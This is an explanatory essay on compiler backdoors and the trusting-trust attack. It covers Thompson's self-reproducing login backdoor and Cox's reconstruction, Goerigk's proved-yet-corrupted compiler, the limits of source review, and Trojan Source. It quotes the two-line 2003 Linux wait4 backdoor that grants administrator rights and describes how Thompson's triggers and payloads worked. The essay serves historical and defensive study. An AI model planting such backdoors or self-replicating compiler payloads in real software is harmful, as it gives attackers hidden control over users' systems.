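# Compiler backdoors and the trusting-trust attack on source-code review

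## Source code, compilers and what a code review assumes

A compiler translates source code, the text programmers write and read, into an executable, the file of machine instructions a computer runs. Someone who controls a compiler can alter it to add hidden behaviour to the programs it builds, while their source code stays clean. In the trusting-trust attack, the altered compiler also adds the alteration to every later version of itself, so its own source code can be clean too. Paul Karger and Roger Schell published the idea in 1974, in a US Air Force evaluation of the Multics operating system. Ken Thompson, co-creator of Unix, made it famous with a lecture he gave in 1983 and published the next year.

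The attack matters because many security evaluations examine source code and assume it accurately represents what the computer runs, as Wheeler (2009) observed in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*. Wheeler's remedy, diverse double-compiling, rebuilds a suspect compiler from source using a second, independent compiler and checks whether the result matches the original bit for bit.

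### From source text to executable

In a set of university lecture slides, Blanton and Alphonce (2023), in *The Compiler and Toolchain*, follow a very small program in the language C through every step of its translation. Without two parameters that it never uses, the program is:

```c
#include <stdio.h>

int main(void) {
    puts("Hello, world!");
    return 0;
}
```

Anyone who has programmed a little can review this program. The first line includes a file of declarations for input and output, `puts` prints a line of text, and the zero at the end conventionally signals that the program finished without error.

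The program that programmers call "the C compiler" is a driver that runs a chain of tools. GCC, the free GNU Compiler Collection, normally preprocesses, compiles, assembles and links code in that order, and a programmer can stop it partway to inspect the output so far.

The preprocessor removes comments, so nothing a programmer wrote in them to reassure a reviewer affects what will run. It also replaces the `#include` line with the contents of the file it names. The output is longer but still C. In Princeton University's *Building C Programs*, a handout that uses a nearly identical program, this output contains declarations of the printing function and many others, but not the code that does the printing.

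Next, the compiler proper turns the C text into assembly language, a written notation for the instructions of one kind of processor. A person with training can still read it. In Blanton and Alphonce's listing, the greeting is stored under the label `.LC0`. The instruction `leaq .LC0(%rip), %rdi` loads its address, and a little further on `call puts@PLT` calls the printing function. A patient reader can match each C statement in a program this small to its instructions. That gets much harder as programs grow, because the compiler must preserve the meaning of the source but can change its structure, sometimes beyond recognition.

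The assembler converts that notation into machine code, the numbers that the processor acts on, and stores them in an object file. Swarthmore College's *Tools for examining different phases of compiling and running a C program* describes this step as close to a one-to-one substitution. The object file contains bytes, so to read it a person needs a disassembler, a program that converts machine code back into assembly, though not into C. In Swarthmore's example, the byte `55` becomes `push %ebp`, and the pair `89 e5` becomes `mov %esp,%ebp`. Function names survive only if the file still has its symbol table, which builders can strip out. The reader also relies on the disassembler, which is itself a compiled program.

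Finally, the linker joins object files to one another and to libraries of ready-made code. The finished executable holds machine code and data, along with a record of the platform it runs on, where execution starts and which libraries it needs. Blanton and Alphonce list the standard C library among the files that the system must load when the greeting program runs. That library contains the instructions behind `puts`, so someone who has read the entire source file still hasn't read the code that puts the words on the screen.

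Review nearly always happens at the top of this chain. In *PW.7*, a practice in the software-development framework of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), code review means that a person looks directly at the code to find problems. The practice covers "human-readable code", which includes source code, scripts and anything else an organisation counts as readable. Reviewers have a good practical reason to work at this level. In Swarthmore College's example, a one-line C function that squares a number becomes twelve bytes of machine code, and a main function of about ten lines becomes 178. A person could check those 190 bytes by hand, but Wheeler judged repeated in-depth review of a production compiler's executable impractical.

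### Compilers that compile themselves

A compiler is itself a program, so its source code also has to be compiled. Many projects write their compiler in the language it compiles. This makes it a self-compiling compiler and raises the question of where the first one came from. When the developers of the Go programming language planned to replace the C programs in their tools with Go programs, they acknowledged in their proposal that building the Go tools from source would then require a working set of Go tools.

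The Go developers keep old versions of the compiler in use to build newer ones. According to Go's installation instructions, Go 1.24 needs at least Go 1.22, which needs Go 1.20, which needs Go 1.17, which needs Go 1.4. The Go 1.4 compiler was the last one written in C, so building it requires a C compiler. If that compiler is GCC, it also had to be built with an earlier compiler. GCC's *Makefile Targets* describes a three-stage build in which the first stage uses whatever compiler the machine already has.

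A person could in principle read all the Go source code back to version 1.4, but building that version requires a C compiler, whose executable came from somewhere else. The build instructions also list other ways to start, such as downloading a recent Go release or installing the Go compiler that comes with GCC, but these too begin with an executable that somebody else built.

Rust, another language, has much the same history. Its first compiler was in OCaml, an older language, and the project abandoned it long ago. According to the chapter *What Bootstrapping does* in the Rust Compiler Development Guide, the standard build now starts by downloading the current beta release of the compiler. In the chapter's worked example:

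1. The downloaded executable, version 1.86.0-beta.1, compiles the source code of version 1.87.0. The output is the "stage 1" compiler.
2. The stage 1 compiler compiles the same source code over again. The output is the "stage 2" compiler, and this is the one that users receive.
3. As an optional test, the stage 2 compiler builds the libraries once more, and the result ought to be the same as before.

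Step 2 repeats the compilation because the old version translated the stage 1 compiler, so the stage 1 executable lacks any improvement in how the new version translates programs, even though it was built from the new source code. Compiling that source again with stage 1 adds the improvements. Further passes should then change nothing, so GCC's build includes a command that compares the last two rounds. This comparison is good at exposing accidental faults, but Wheeler points out that a maliciously altered compiler can pass it.

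Programmers build each new compiler executable by compiling the new source code with an older executable, a procedure they call bootstrapping. A source review covers only the source code.

### Backdoors, and the assumption behind a review

NIST's glossary defines a *backdoor* as any undocumented way of gaining access to a computer system. Writers on compilers need a slightly more specific definition: hidden behaviour that gives an attacker access or control under a condition the attacker chose. That condition is the trigger, and the payload is the behaviour it sets off or, strictly, the code that carries it out.

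Wheeler recounts a case with both a trigger and a payload. Around 1994, a developer at the software company Borland added an account to its database server, Interbase, with the user name "politically" and the password "correct". The account was undocumented, normal commands could not change it, and it gave whoever used it complete control. Logging in with those credentials was the trigger, and the grant of control was the payload. Every other login worked normally, so an ordinary test of the login procedure would have found nothing wrong unless the tester happened to try that pair of words.

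Borland published Interbase's source code in July 2000, and outside developers found the backdoor account in less than six months. Jim Starkey, who had launched Interbase but left before the account was added, believed it was only meant to let one part of the software communicate with another. He may well have been right, but the account still left users' databases open from 1994 to 2001.

Unlike the Interbase backdoor, a compiler backdoor does not appear in the source code, where a reader could find it. Wheeler describes this situation in terms of correspondence. An executable corresponds to a piece of source code if and only if running it always produces the behaviour that the source code specifies, provided that the machine and surrounding software work correctly. Wheeler calls an executable that fails this test corrupted, whether the cause is an accident or an attack.

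An executable corresponds to its source code if it behaves as the source specifies, whatever its exact sequence of bits. Two compilers without backdoors will almost certainly turn the same source code into different executables, and both executables can correspond to it. No general procedure can decide whether two different executables always behave alike, but a computer can quickly check whether two files are identical. Much of the defensive work on compilers therefore tries to replace comparisons of behaviour with checks for identical files.

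The easy comparison requires a deterministic compiler, one that always gives the same output for the same inputs. A compiler may not be deterministic, for instance because it writes the build time into the executable or because the order in which parallel tasks finish affects the result. *Definitions*, published by Reproducible Builds, a project that promotes checkable builds of free software, defines a build as reproducible if anyone with the same source code, build environment and instructions can recreate the output bit for bit. This standard is harder to meet than it sounds. Wheeler found that rebuilding a compiler from its original build instructions often gave a different file, in many cases because the organisation's records left out something that had affected the build.

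Every source review assumes that the executable corresponds to the source code, which the review itself cannot test. For most software in daily use, people accept this without checking. Reproducible Builds describes how, with free software, anyone may inspect the source code, but most users receive a ready-made executable and cannot confirm that the two match. If an attacker changes the executable during the build and leaves the source code alone, the change is practically invisible to both the program's authors and its users.

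A reviewer who wants to vouch for a running program therefore has to establish both that the source code is benign and that the running program corresponds to it. Establishing one does not establish the other. Interbase's source code itself contained the backdoor, and nothing suggests that the executable departed from that source code. In a trusting-trust attack, the source code can be clean while the computer runs something else. Wheeler notes that diverse double-compiling can show that a compiler's executable corresponds to its source code, but that somebody must still read that source code to learn whether it is malicious.

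Recompiling source code and comparing the result with the distributed executable can reveal that an attacker has simply replaced the executable, if the build is deterministic. But the check is only as reliable as the compiler it uses. Security writers call a component "trusted" if people rely on it and "trustworthy" if it deserves that reliance. Everyone who compiles a program trusts a compiler, whether or not they have any evidence that it is trustworthy.

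### Language models as producers

Artificial intelligence raises a similar difficulty. A language model is a program that takes in text and continues it, one small piece at a time. Its output depends on its weights, which in a large model are billions of numbers. No programmer chooses these numbers; training sets them by running the model on many examples or tasks and gradually adjusting the weights so that its output scores better. Developers often use one model's outputs as training examples for another, a practice called distillation when the aim is to pass on the first model's abilities. Many models also write out intermediate steps before answering. This text is the model's visible reasoning, and its faithfulness is the degree to which it reports what determined the answer.

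People can read a model's visible reasoning and the code it writes far more easily than they can read its weights. But they may know little about the training that shaped that reasoning and code, or have reason to doubt it. So the question Thompson's lecture raised about compilers also applies to models: can reading a product give assurance when nobody has good grounds to trust its producer?

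## How a compiler can hide and reproduce a backdoor

### The Air Force report

Multics was the most secure operating system on the market in the early 1970s, but Karger and Schell broke into it in several ways. Their 1974 report for the US Air Force, reprinted with a commentary in *Thirty Years Later* (Karger and Schell, 2002), also considered how an intruder could keep access after the first break-in.

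An intruder who relies on an existing flaw loses access when someone fixes it. The report's alternative was to install a "trap door", an older term for a backdoor, preferably in the executable, where nobody reading the source code would see it. But recompiling the affected part of the system from clean source removes such a trap door. The Pentagon's contract for Multics required the manufacturer, Honeywell, to deliver the source code so that the Pentagon could recompile it.

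The report describes how a trap door could survive recompilation. Most of the supervisor, the most privileged part of Multics, was written in PL/I. An intruder could alter the PL/I compiler to detect when it was compiling part of the supervisor and add a trap door to the output, while leaving the added code out of the printed listing. Because the compiler was also written in PL/I, the altered version could insert the same alteration when compiling its own next version. A footnote adds that an altered assembler would work just as well.

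Karger and Schell did not build this compiler. They guessed that it would cost perhaps five times the figures in their cost table, which lists 18 hours of work and $80 of computer time for an ordinary trap door in one supervisor routine. If they meant that entry, the compiler version would have needed about 90 hours and $400. They wrote that even costs several hundred times those in the table would be nominal to a foreign agent.

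Paul Karger and Roger Schell tested whether a manufacturer would distribute a trap door without noticing it. They planted one in the Multics development system at MIT, leaving it one instruction short of being harmful, and Honeywell shipped it to the Pentagon. No one found it until about a year after their 1974 report came out, when auditors at General Motors, another Multics customer, noticed an odd error code it returned.

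Thompson got the idea for his compiler backdoor from Karger and Schell's report. By the time of his lecture he could no longer identify the report and cited an "unknown Air Force document", so Karger and Schell sent him a new copy.

### A program that prints itself

The 1974 report does not explain how the compiler trap door would copy itself, which is the harder part of the attack. The compiler has to pass on the code that adds the backdoor, then the code that adds that code, and so on, which may seem endless.

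Thompson (1984), in *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, approached the problem through a puzzle from his college days: write a program whose output is an exact copy of its own source code. His printed example is in C and runs to more than 200 lines. Cox (2023), in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*, gives one that fits on a single line of the language Python:

```python
s='s=%r;print(s%%s)';print(s%s)
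```

The first statement, up to the second semicolon, stores a piece of text under the name `s`. The second statement prints that text after filling in its placeholder. In Python, `s%s` means "take the text `s` and put `s` into it". The placeholder `%r` stands for the inserted text in quotation marks, and `%%` is the way to write an ordinary percent sign. Python therefore works through the stored text like this:

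| Part of the stored text | What Python prints |
|---|---|
| `s=` | `s=` |
| `%r` | `'s=%r;print(s%%s)'` |
| `;print(s` | `;print(s` |
| `%%` | `%` |
| `s)` | `s)` |

Joining the entries in the right-hand column gives the program. The regress stops because the program uses the same text twice, as a template for the output and as the material inserted into that template.

Thompson pointed out two properties of such programs that he needed later. Another program can easily write one, and it can carry any amount of extra material, which it will reproduce along with the rest. The Python line can carry a comment, for instance, if the comment also goes into the stored text:

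```python
s='s=%r;print(s%%s) # hello';print(s%s) # hello
```

This version prints itself too, comment included. The extra material could equally be instructions for altering a login program.

### A value that only the executable contains

Thompson's next step involves nothing malicious. In C, a programmer writes `\n` inside a piece of text to start a new line, and the compiler has to turn those two characters into a single number, which is 10 in the standard ASCII code. Cox gives a simplified version of the part of a C compiler that does this:

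```c
c = next();
if(c == '\\') {
    c = next();
    if(c == 'n')
        c = '\n';
}
```

When the compiler reads a backslash followed by an `n`, it produces the new-line character. But the last line of the code writes that character as `'\n'`, the same notation the code is supposed to interpret, and the number 10 appears nowhere in the code. The code works because the older compiler that translates it already replaces `'\n'` with 10, and so puts a 10 into the new executable.

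No compiler can do this the first time. The programmer has to write `c = 10`, compile the compiler, install the result, and only then change the source to `c = '\n'`. From then on, the number passes from each executable to the next. Thompson's own example was adding `\v`, the vertical tab. The existing compiler rejects the new source, so the programmer puts in the number 11 for one round of compilation and then removes it. Thompson wrote that this was as close to a "learning" program as he had seen.

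The source code of a self-compiling compiler can therefore omit something that all its executables contain. For example, a reader of the C compiler's source could look up the character code for a new line in an ASCII table, but could not work it out from the source alone.

### Two targets

Thompson then used the same method to pass on a backdoor. He first altered the C compiler to check for a pattern in the source code of `login`, the Unix program that asks users for their passwords. When the compiler found the pattern, it produced a slightly different program, which accepted either the user's real password or a fixed one that Thompson knew. On its own, this alteration would not have lasted, because anyone glancing through the compiler's source code would have seen it.

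He therefore added an alteration with the compiler itself as its target. When the compiler found a pattern from its own source code, it inserted both alterations, using the self-printing technique. The procedure is the one for `\n`:

1. Add both alterations to the compiler's source code and compile it with the clean compiler.
2. Install the resulting executable as the official compiler.
3. Delete the alterations from the source code.
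4. Whenever anyone compiles the clean source code, the installed executable puts both alterations back.

After that, `login` has a backdoor that appears in neither program's source code. Thompson therefore concluded that no amount of source-level scrutiny would protect a user from untrusted code.

### The surviving code

The lecture describes the altered compiler only in outline. At a conference in March 2023, Thompson said that he still had the code and that nobody had ever asked for it. Cox, a developer of the Go language, watched the recording that September and asked. Thompson sent him a file called `nih.a`, for "not invented here". *trusting trust code* (Cox, 2023), which announced Cox's annotated version, reported that the code had been in a public archive of Unix history since that summer and that no one had noticed.

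The backdoor consists of 99 lines of C and a 20-line script. Cox had expected it to work on an internal representation deep in the compiler and was surprised at how simple it was. The altered compiler calls a function named `codenih` every time it reads a line of source code. The function skips any tabs at the start and compares what follows with a few fixed strings. If one matches, the function adds text to the end of the line before compilation continues, without changing the file on disk.

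| Line that matches | Condition | What the altered compiler does |
|---|---|---|
| `namep = crypt(pwbuf);` | none | adds the password backdoor |
| `av[4] = "-P";` | none | sets a counter to 1 |
| `while(getline()) {` | counter is 1 | adds a call to `codenih`; counter becomes 2 |
| `fflush(obuf);` | counter is 2 | adds a call to a function named `repronih`; counter becomes 3 |

The first line in the table comes from `login.c` and encrypts the password the user typed. The code added after that line checks whether the password was "codenih". If so, it moves two pointers to the ends of the strings that `login` is about to compare, so the comparison succeeds. Any other password goes through the normal check.

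The other three lines are in `cc.c`, the part of the compiler that reads and preprocesses source code. Together they restore the two calls that the altered compiler needs, but the new compiler also needs the functions themselves. When the compiler reaches the end of a file, it runs `repronih`, which acts only if the counter is 3. It then writes out the complete source of the backdoor, including its own, as though that text had always been at the end of `cc.c`.

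This is the Python trick with numbers instead of quoted text. The backdoor's source contains a long list of byte values that encode the source, with a percent sign marking where the list belongs. `repronih` prints the text before the mark, then the list, then the text after the mark. The 20-line script creates the list the first time.

The compiler had an option to print its preprocessed text instead of compiling it, and the inserted lines would have appeared in that output. `codenih` therefore returns immediately when the option is on.

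Cox ran all this on a simulator of Sixth Edition Unix. Compiling the clean source with the clean compiler gave an executable of 10,724 bytes. Compiling the altered source with the clean compiler gave 12,918 bytes, about a fifth more. Compiling the clean source with the altered compiler also gave 12,918 bytes. The two larger executables differed only in the source file name that each contained. After one more round of compilation this difference disappeared, so a comparison of successive builds, like the one GCC's developers use, would not have revealed the backdoor.

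He then installed the altered compiler, rebuilt both the compiler and `login` from their clean source code, and logged in as the system administrator with the password "codenih".

Cox also wrote a version for the Go compiler. Go's compiler reads source files through a routine called `Parse`, and he added code that changes the text before `Parse` reads it. This code makes a program that should print "hello, world" print "backdoored!" instead. When the compiler reads the file that defines `Parse`, the code inserts itself again. Cox compiled the modified compiler, discarded his changes to the source, and rebuilt the compiler from the clean version. The greeting program still printed "backdoored!". He argues, however, that such a backdoor could not hide in Go's official chain of builds from older releases.

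### What happened at Bell Labs

Thompson also used his altered compiler on colleagues. The surviving code dates from between June 1974 and June 1975. It could not have worked on Fifth Edition Unix, released in June 1974, because that version preprocessed only files beginning with the character `#`. The Fifth Edition's `cc.c` did not begin with `#`, so the altered compiler would have left its own source untouched. The files in the archive were last modified on 19 June 1975. Cox's best guess is that the code dates from early that year.

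The target was the group at Bell Labs that developed the Programmer's Workbench, or PWB, a version of Unix for large software projects. John Mashey, who worked there, says in the Computer History Museum's *Oral History of John Mashey* (2018) that the group got new software by having someone drive to the research site at Murray Hill, get onto Thompson's machine and copy whatever was new. They had to take executables as well as source code because Dennis Ritchie, the creator of C, kept adding features to the language and then rewriting software to use them, and the older compilers could not compile the result. `\v` needed a special round of compilation for the same reason.

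Thompson told the 2023 audience that he had either released the compiler to the group or "got somebody to steal it", and then tracked whether the group found the backdoor. Eventually PWB's `login` was altered too.

In *Thompson trojan put into practice*, a message to a Unix history mailing list, Thompson (2021) recalled that when PWB recompiled the compiler, it came out one byte larger, and another byte larger the next time. The extra byte, he wrote, "was my bug". According to Cox, each generation added one zero byte to a piece of stored text. Executables on that system always had an even number of bytes, so the file must have grown by two bytes every second recompilation. The surviving code does not have this fault, and Thompson did not keep the version that did.

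By Thompson's account, the PWB programmers noticed that the compiler was growing and experimented with it until they broke its ability to reproduce the backdoor. He was unsure whether they ever realised what they had found, and in 2023 he said that they had not. Wheeler's dissertation says that the attack "was never detected", and many retellings agree, but this is wrong or at least badly incomplete.

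People on the receiving end remember more. Mashey says that a colleague, he thinks his officemate, found a function name in the executable that was nowhere in the source code. Mashey then went onto Thompson's machine and found the backdoor. Linderman's reply in the same discussion, *Thompson trojan put into practice* (2021), named the colleague as Larry Wehr. Linderman thought Wehr had used `nm`, which lists the names in an executable, possibly because of the extra bytes. He added that they might never have noticed if Thompson had not divided his code so neatly into functions. Doug McIlroy, whose message Thompson was answering, also believed that PWB had found the backdoor without looking for one.

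The surviving code fits this story, since `codenih` and `repronih` are separate functions whose names do not appear in the clean source. The recollections are more than forty years old, and former colleagues may have influenced one another's memories. Still, Mashey describes something he did himself, while Thompson was outside the group and was inferring what it had understood. Somebody at PWB probably did recognise the backdoor.

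The oldest account has another ending. In *Joy of reproduction*, a message posted to a public network a year before the lecture, Ritchie (1982) says that "we" installed the altered preprocessor on another system at Bell Labs. It lasted several months, until someone copied a clean executable from a different machine. Ritchie mentions neither growth nor discovery. The stories may not conflict, since a group whose compiler behaved strangely would have had good reason to fetch a fresh copy.

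Wheeler has since corrected his statement on *David A. Wheeler’s Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, citing Thompson's message, but says he has no evidence that anybody recognised the problem as an attack. He also warns against expecting the next attacker to make the same mistake. An attacker can easily test for it by having the altered compiler rebuild itself and checking that the file stays the same.

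Cox compared many versions of the story and concluded that the victim was PWB, although CNCF's *“Unix Support Group” event*, an entry in a catalogue of software supply-chain compromises, names a different Bell Labs group. According to one rumour, the altered `login` escaped to the company BBN, where someone used it to log in under the name "kt". Thompson told Cox that this could not have happened, and Cox points out that the backdoor doesn't create an account, since "codenih" works only as a password for an existing one.

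### The story of the disassembler

In a common version of the story, Thompson also altered the tools used to inspect the executable. Schneier wrote in *Countering “Trusting Trust”* (2006) that the victim noticed nothing even after disassembling the compiler, because the compiler had "rigged the disassembler, too". Wheeler says in one chapter that Thompson's demonstration subverted the disassembler, and elsewhere that it subverted the symbolic debugger, a tool for examining a program as it runs.

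The surviving code matches lines from `login.c` and `cc.c` and from no other program, and its only attempt at concealment is to do nothing when someone asks for the preprocessed text. Thompson's printed lecture doesn't mention an altered disassembler. He says in it that he could have used an assembler, a loader or even the processor's microcode instead of the compiler, and that a backdoor is harder to detect at lower levels, but he doesn't say that he tried any of these.

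PWB received a somewhat different version of the code, so nobody can rule out that this version had another target. But if Wehr did find the suspicious name with `nm`, at least that tool still listed names accurately.

The compiler could also insert a backdoor into the disassembler. It would need another trigger, for the disassembler's source code, and a payload that made the disassembler skip the added instructions. The attack would then have to keep working as the disassembler, `login` and the compiler changed.

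### How the attack breaks

Thompson's triggers are exact pieces of text, so they stop matching when the text changes. If a programmer had renamed `pwbuf` in `login.c`, or indented that line with spaces instead of tabs, the next `login` executable would have been clean. A change to the line `av[4] = "-P";` would have silently ended the attack, because the counter would have stayed at zero and the next compiler would have been built without the backdoor.

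A change to `fflush(obuf);` would have been more awkward for Thompson. The altered compiler adds a call to `codenih` before it reaches that line, but it adds the function itself only if the line matches. If the line had changed, the linker would have stopped with an error about a missing function called `codenih`, and the programmer would not have found that name in the source code.

Cox's Go version can fail in a similar way. It finds the compiler by one piece of text and hooks itself in by replacing another. If only the second piece changed, the new compiler would contain the whole backdoor but never run it, and the compiler after that would be clean.

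A trigger can also match the wrong program. Many programs that read text might contain `while(getline()) {`, so Thompson's code ignores this line unless the much rarer `av[4] = "-P";` has come first. The `login` trigger has no such safeguard. Its payload uses variables named `np` and `c`, so another program with the same trigger line but without those variables would have failed to compile for no visible reason.

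A more specific trigger is less likely to match the wrong code, but an ordinary edit is more likely to disable it. Thompson's trigger requires three lines of the compiler to match in order, so changing any one of them disables it. This was a real danger because Ritchie was revising the compiler so often.

An attacker who wanted a backdoor to last could use several narrow triggers. Each would match a different distinctive passage in the compiler's source and insert the entire backdoor at its own location, so any one of them would be enough to reproduce it. If an edit disabled one trigger, the others would still copy every trigger into the next compiler, including the disabled one, which would work again if someone undid the edit. The attacker could protect the `login` backdoor in the same way, with payloads for two or three different parts of the program.

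The self-printing technique can carry more triggers without changes, because it reproduces whatever extra material it contains. The triggers must be coordinated, or two that matched at once would insert the same functions twice and the compilation would fail. Extra triggers also make the executable larger, and Thompson's, with a single set, was already a fifth larger than the clean one.

Extra triggers help the backdoor survive changes to the source code, but they do not help if someone replaces the altered compiler with a clean executable from another machine. According to Ritchie, this happened at Bell Labs.

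## What reading the source can and cannot establish

Most users have no clean executable to fall back on. If they doubt a program, they can read its source code and rebuild it, but Thompson's moral was that this would not protect them. He stated it without qualification, based on a single attack. How far the moral holds depends on whether the attacker has altered the compiler or written source code that misleads its readers.

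### Rebuilding with a corrupted compiler

If a compiler is corrupted but its source code is clean, rebuilding from source with that compiler does not help. Wheeler finds that several variations on this idea only move the attack elsewhere. Users who switch to an interpreted language, in which another program runs the source code directly, still need an interpreter that somebody compiled. Reading the current source code also does not show what earlier versions contained. An attacker could add the alteration to the source code of one release and delete it from the next. Anyone who had compiled the first release would then build the second with a corrupted compiler, and a reader of the second release's source code would find nothing wrong.

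GCC's comparison of its last two builds is a version of a stricter check, which the computer scientist Niklaus Wirth proposed in a textbook: the compiler has to reproduce itself. Write c(s, m) for the executable that results when compiler m translates source code s. Let s be the compiler's own source code and b whatever compiler the developer already has. The developer builds three executables:

```
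m0 = c(s, b)
m1 = c(s, m0)
m2 = c(s, m1)
```

The compiler passes if m1 and m2 are identical, bit for bit.

Wolfgang Goerigk, a computer scientist at the University of Kiel, proved a theorem, restated by Wheeler, that m1 and m2 must be identical in this test if b and s are correct, the compiler is deterministic, every compilation finishes and the hardware works. A correct b produces an m0 that behaves as s specifies, although b may generate different instructions than s would. When m0 compiles s, it therefore outputs the file that s specifies, which is m1. Because m1 also behaves as s specifies, it outputs the same file when it compiles s, and that file is m2.

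The converse of the theorem is false. A mismatch reveals a fault somewhere, which makes the test useful, but a match can occur even when b, s or both are faulty. For example, a compiler with no backdoor may mistranslate a language feature and still pass if its own source code never uses that feature.

A corrupted compiler can easily pass a test that checks whether successive builds match. Suppose an executable b outputs a copy of itself whenever its input is the compiler's source, s. Compiling s with b produces m0, compiling s with m0 produces m1, and compiling s with m1 produces m2, so all three are identical to b. Thompson's compiler also reproduced itself in Cox's simulation, once the stray file name was gone.

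Goerigk and Langmaack (2003) point out in *Will Informatics Be Able to Justify the Construction of Large Computer Based Systems?* that such a compiler needs to mistranslate only two programs, the attacker's target and the compiler's own source code.

Developers also run compilers on large suites of test programs, but a suite could expose this compiler only if it included one of those two programs. The compiler's own source code is an obvious choice, but the tester would have to compare the output with a translation already known to be correct. Goerigk and Langmaack doubted that anyone had ever verified an existing compiler executable in this way.

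### A proved compiler that is still malicious

*Compiler Verification Revisited* (Goerigk, 2000) showed that a compiler's executable can be incorrect even when its source code has been mathematically proved correct. Such a proof is about the most thorough scrutiny source code can receive.

Goerigk wrote a compiler for a small language based on Lisp, and a simulator for a simple machine to run its output. He used ACL2, a program that checks mathematical proofs and partly automates them, to prove the compiler's source code correct. Here, "correct" means that if a source program is well formed and its translation gives a result, that result is the one the source program specifies. The compiler can be correct in this sense even if a translation runs forever. Würthinger (2006) works through Goerigk's example in a bachelor's thesis, *Formal Compiler Verification with ACL2*. The proof needed more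 than 100 theorems and was more complex than the compiler.

Goerigk also constructed a corrupted executable to go with this source code. In Würthinger's version, it treats its input in one of three ways:

1. If the input is the source code of the correct compiler, it outputs a copy of itself.
2. If the input is the source code of a login program, it outputs something harmful.
3. For any other input, it does what the correct compiler would do.

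The copying works like Cox's one-line Python program, with the number 2000 as the placeholder. The code has to refer to the placeholder without containing another copy of it, so it writes the number as 1999 + 1.

A developer who compiles the proved source code with this executable gets back the corrupted compiler, which passes the self-reproduction test. The proof remains valid, but it is about the source code, and the program on the machine is not a translation of that source code. In his slides for a workshop talk, *Proving Preservation of Partial Correctness with ACL2*, Goerigk (2000) listed the insufficiency of source-level verification and testing as a fact he had proved mechanically. Wheeler later used Goerigk's pair of compilers to try out diverse double-compiling.

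Würthinger's example shows that such a compiler can exist, but it doesn't show that the compiler would last. Its triggers compare whole programs, so any change to the compiler's source code would disable them. Thompson's triggers matched only a few lines, so they were much less likely to be disabled by an edit.

Reading source code can also reveal ordinary mistakes. The compiler listing printed in Würthinger's thesis translates the "then" branch of every conditional twice and never translates the "else" branch, which a reader can notice in a few minutes. This is presumably a copying error, since a compiler with that fault could not have satisfied the correctness theorem, so the printed text is probably not the text that ACL2 checked.

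### Reading the executable instead

A determined reviewer could read the executable instead of the source code. Goerigk recommended a similar approach, comparing the compiler's executable with its source code to confirm that each part was translated correctly. Doing this by hand is impractical for a production compiler, and Wheeler points out that a tool to automate it would be about as complex as a compiler and would need revising whenever the compiler changed.

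One person could have read all of Thompson's altered compiler, but modern compilers are far larger. *Deniable Backdoors Using Compiler Bugs* (Bauer, Cuoq and Regehr, 2015) reports that GCC contained roughly 11,000 assertions, statements that only check whether the compiler's internal data are in order.

Reading only part of the source can reveal a backdoor, especially when the reader can compare it with clean source code. This is how the Programmer's Workbench group recognised a function name that did not belong. Wheeler describes ways to automate this kind of search. A program can look for stored text that resembles a password or cryptographic key, for network calls in software that doesn't need a network, or for requests for the date, which may belong to a backdoor that waits for a particular day. But an attacker can run the same searches first and revise the backdoor until the searches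 find nothing.

Copying the executable to an unrelated machine would get round an altered disassembler, but it might not get round an altered operating system, which could show a clean copy of the compiler to anyone who opens the file and still run a different one. Wheeler's remedy is to shut the machine down and read its storage directly. Thompson thought that a well-installed backdoor in microcode, the low-level instructions that control how a processor carries out its machine code, would be "almost impossible to detect".

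### What undecidability rules out

Searching for malicious code also has a theoretical limit. Wheeler, citing Fred Cohen's early work on computer viruses, says that no pattern can match all malicious programs without also matching some harmless ones. A stronger claim is that no checker can correctly report, for every program, whether it is malicious. The usual argument is by contradiction. If such a checker existed, someone could write a program that contains the checker and runs it on the program's own text. The program would delete the user's files if the checker reported "harmless" and do nothing if it reported "malicious". Either report would be wrong, so no such checker can exist.

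The argument above rules out a checker that is right about every possible program, but not one that is right about many programs and answers "don't know" about the rest. Nor does it make any particular program unknowable. Goerigk's proof answered a question about one compiler, even though no general procedure can answer that question for every compiler. A reviewer can also reject any program that is too convoluted to follow, including the one used in that argument.

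Thompson's attack escapes a source review because the source code of his compiler was clean, not because of undecidability. Even a perfect checker, which undecidability rules out, would have correctly classified that source code as harmless.

### Source code that misleads its readers

Now suppose that the compiler is honest and the attacker can change only the source code. Everything harmful is then in the text that reviewers read, but they may still miss it. In November 2003, developers found two extra lines in a copy of the source code of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system:

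```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

According to *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, a blog post from Princeton's Center for Information Technology Policy, an expert who read the backdoor code casually would take it for routine error-checking. The code seems to make the function `wait4` return an error if a program calls it with a forbidden combination of options. But in C, `==` compares two values and `=` assigns one, and the code uses `=`. When a program calls `wait4` with those options, the code therefore sets the user's identification number to 0 instead of testing whether it is 0. That number belongs to the administrator and gives access to everything. Because C treats an assignment of 0 as false, the second line, which would return the error, never runs, and the caller gets no error.

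Szepe (2003), replying on the kernel mailing list, pointed out the parentheses around the assignment, which prevent a GCC warning. The line would not have compiled without them, so they aren't proof of anything.

The first clue came from record-keeping rather than from reading the code. Linux developers kept the master copy in a system called BitKeeper, where each change came with a pointer to a record of its approval. The attacker had apparently broken into a server that held a second copy, and Larry McVoy noticed a change there without a pointer. Once the two lines were on the mailing list, one developer remarked that they looked odd, and another, Chad Kitching, recognised that they set the user number to zero and suspected a backdoor. McVoy (2003), in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, agreed and admitted that he had missed it. Reviewers understood the code quickly, but by then they had only two lines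 to read and a good reason to be suspicious.

Programmers have also held contests in writing such code, including the Obfuscated V contest of 2004 and the Underhanded C contest of 2005. Wheeler thinks simple measures would defeat many of the known tricks. Some depend on layout, such as code that looks like a comment or is indented so far that an editor does not show it. Reformatting the source before review exposes these. Others depend on well-known mistakes like the one in the Linux code, which tools can highlight and language rules can forbid.

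An attacker can pass off a small deliberate bug as an accident, because anyone might make the same mistake. A trusting-trust attack in a compiler's source code would be harder to explain as a typing error, because it needs far more than one wrong character.

### Text that appears in a different order

Some misleading code appears on the screen in a different order from the one stored in the file. *Trojan Source* (Boucher and Anderson, 2023) describes an attack, first made public in 2021, in which a reviewer and a compiler read the same characters in different orders. The attack uses invisible control characters that Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes for languages written from right to left. These characters change the order in which a screen displays text but not the order in which the file stores it.

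Boucher and Anderson explain the trick with letters:

| Stored in the file | Control characters | Displayed |
|---|---|---|
| a b c | right-to-left around the whole | c b a |
| a b c d e f | right-to-left around the whole, left-to-right around each group of three | d e f a b c |

The second arrangement is the useful one for an attacker, because each group remains legible while the groups trade places.

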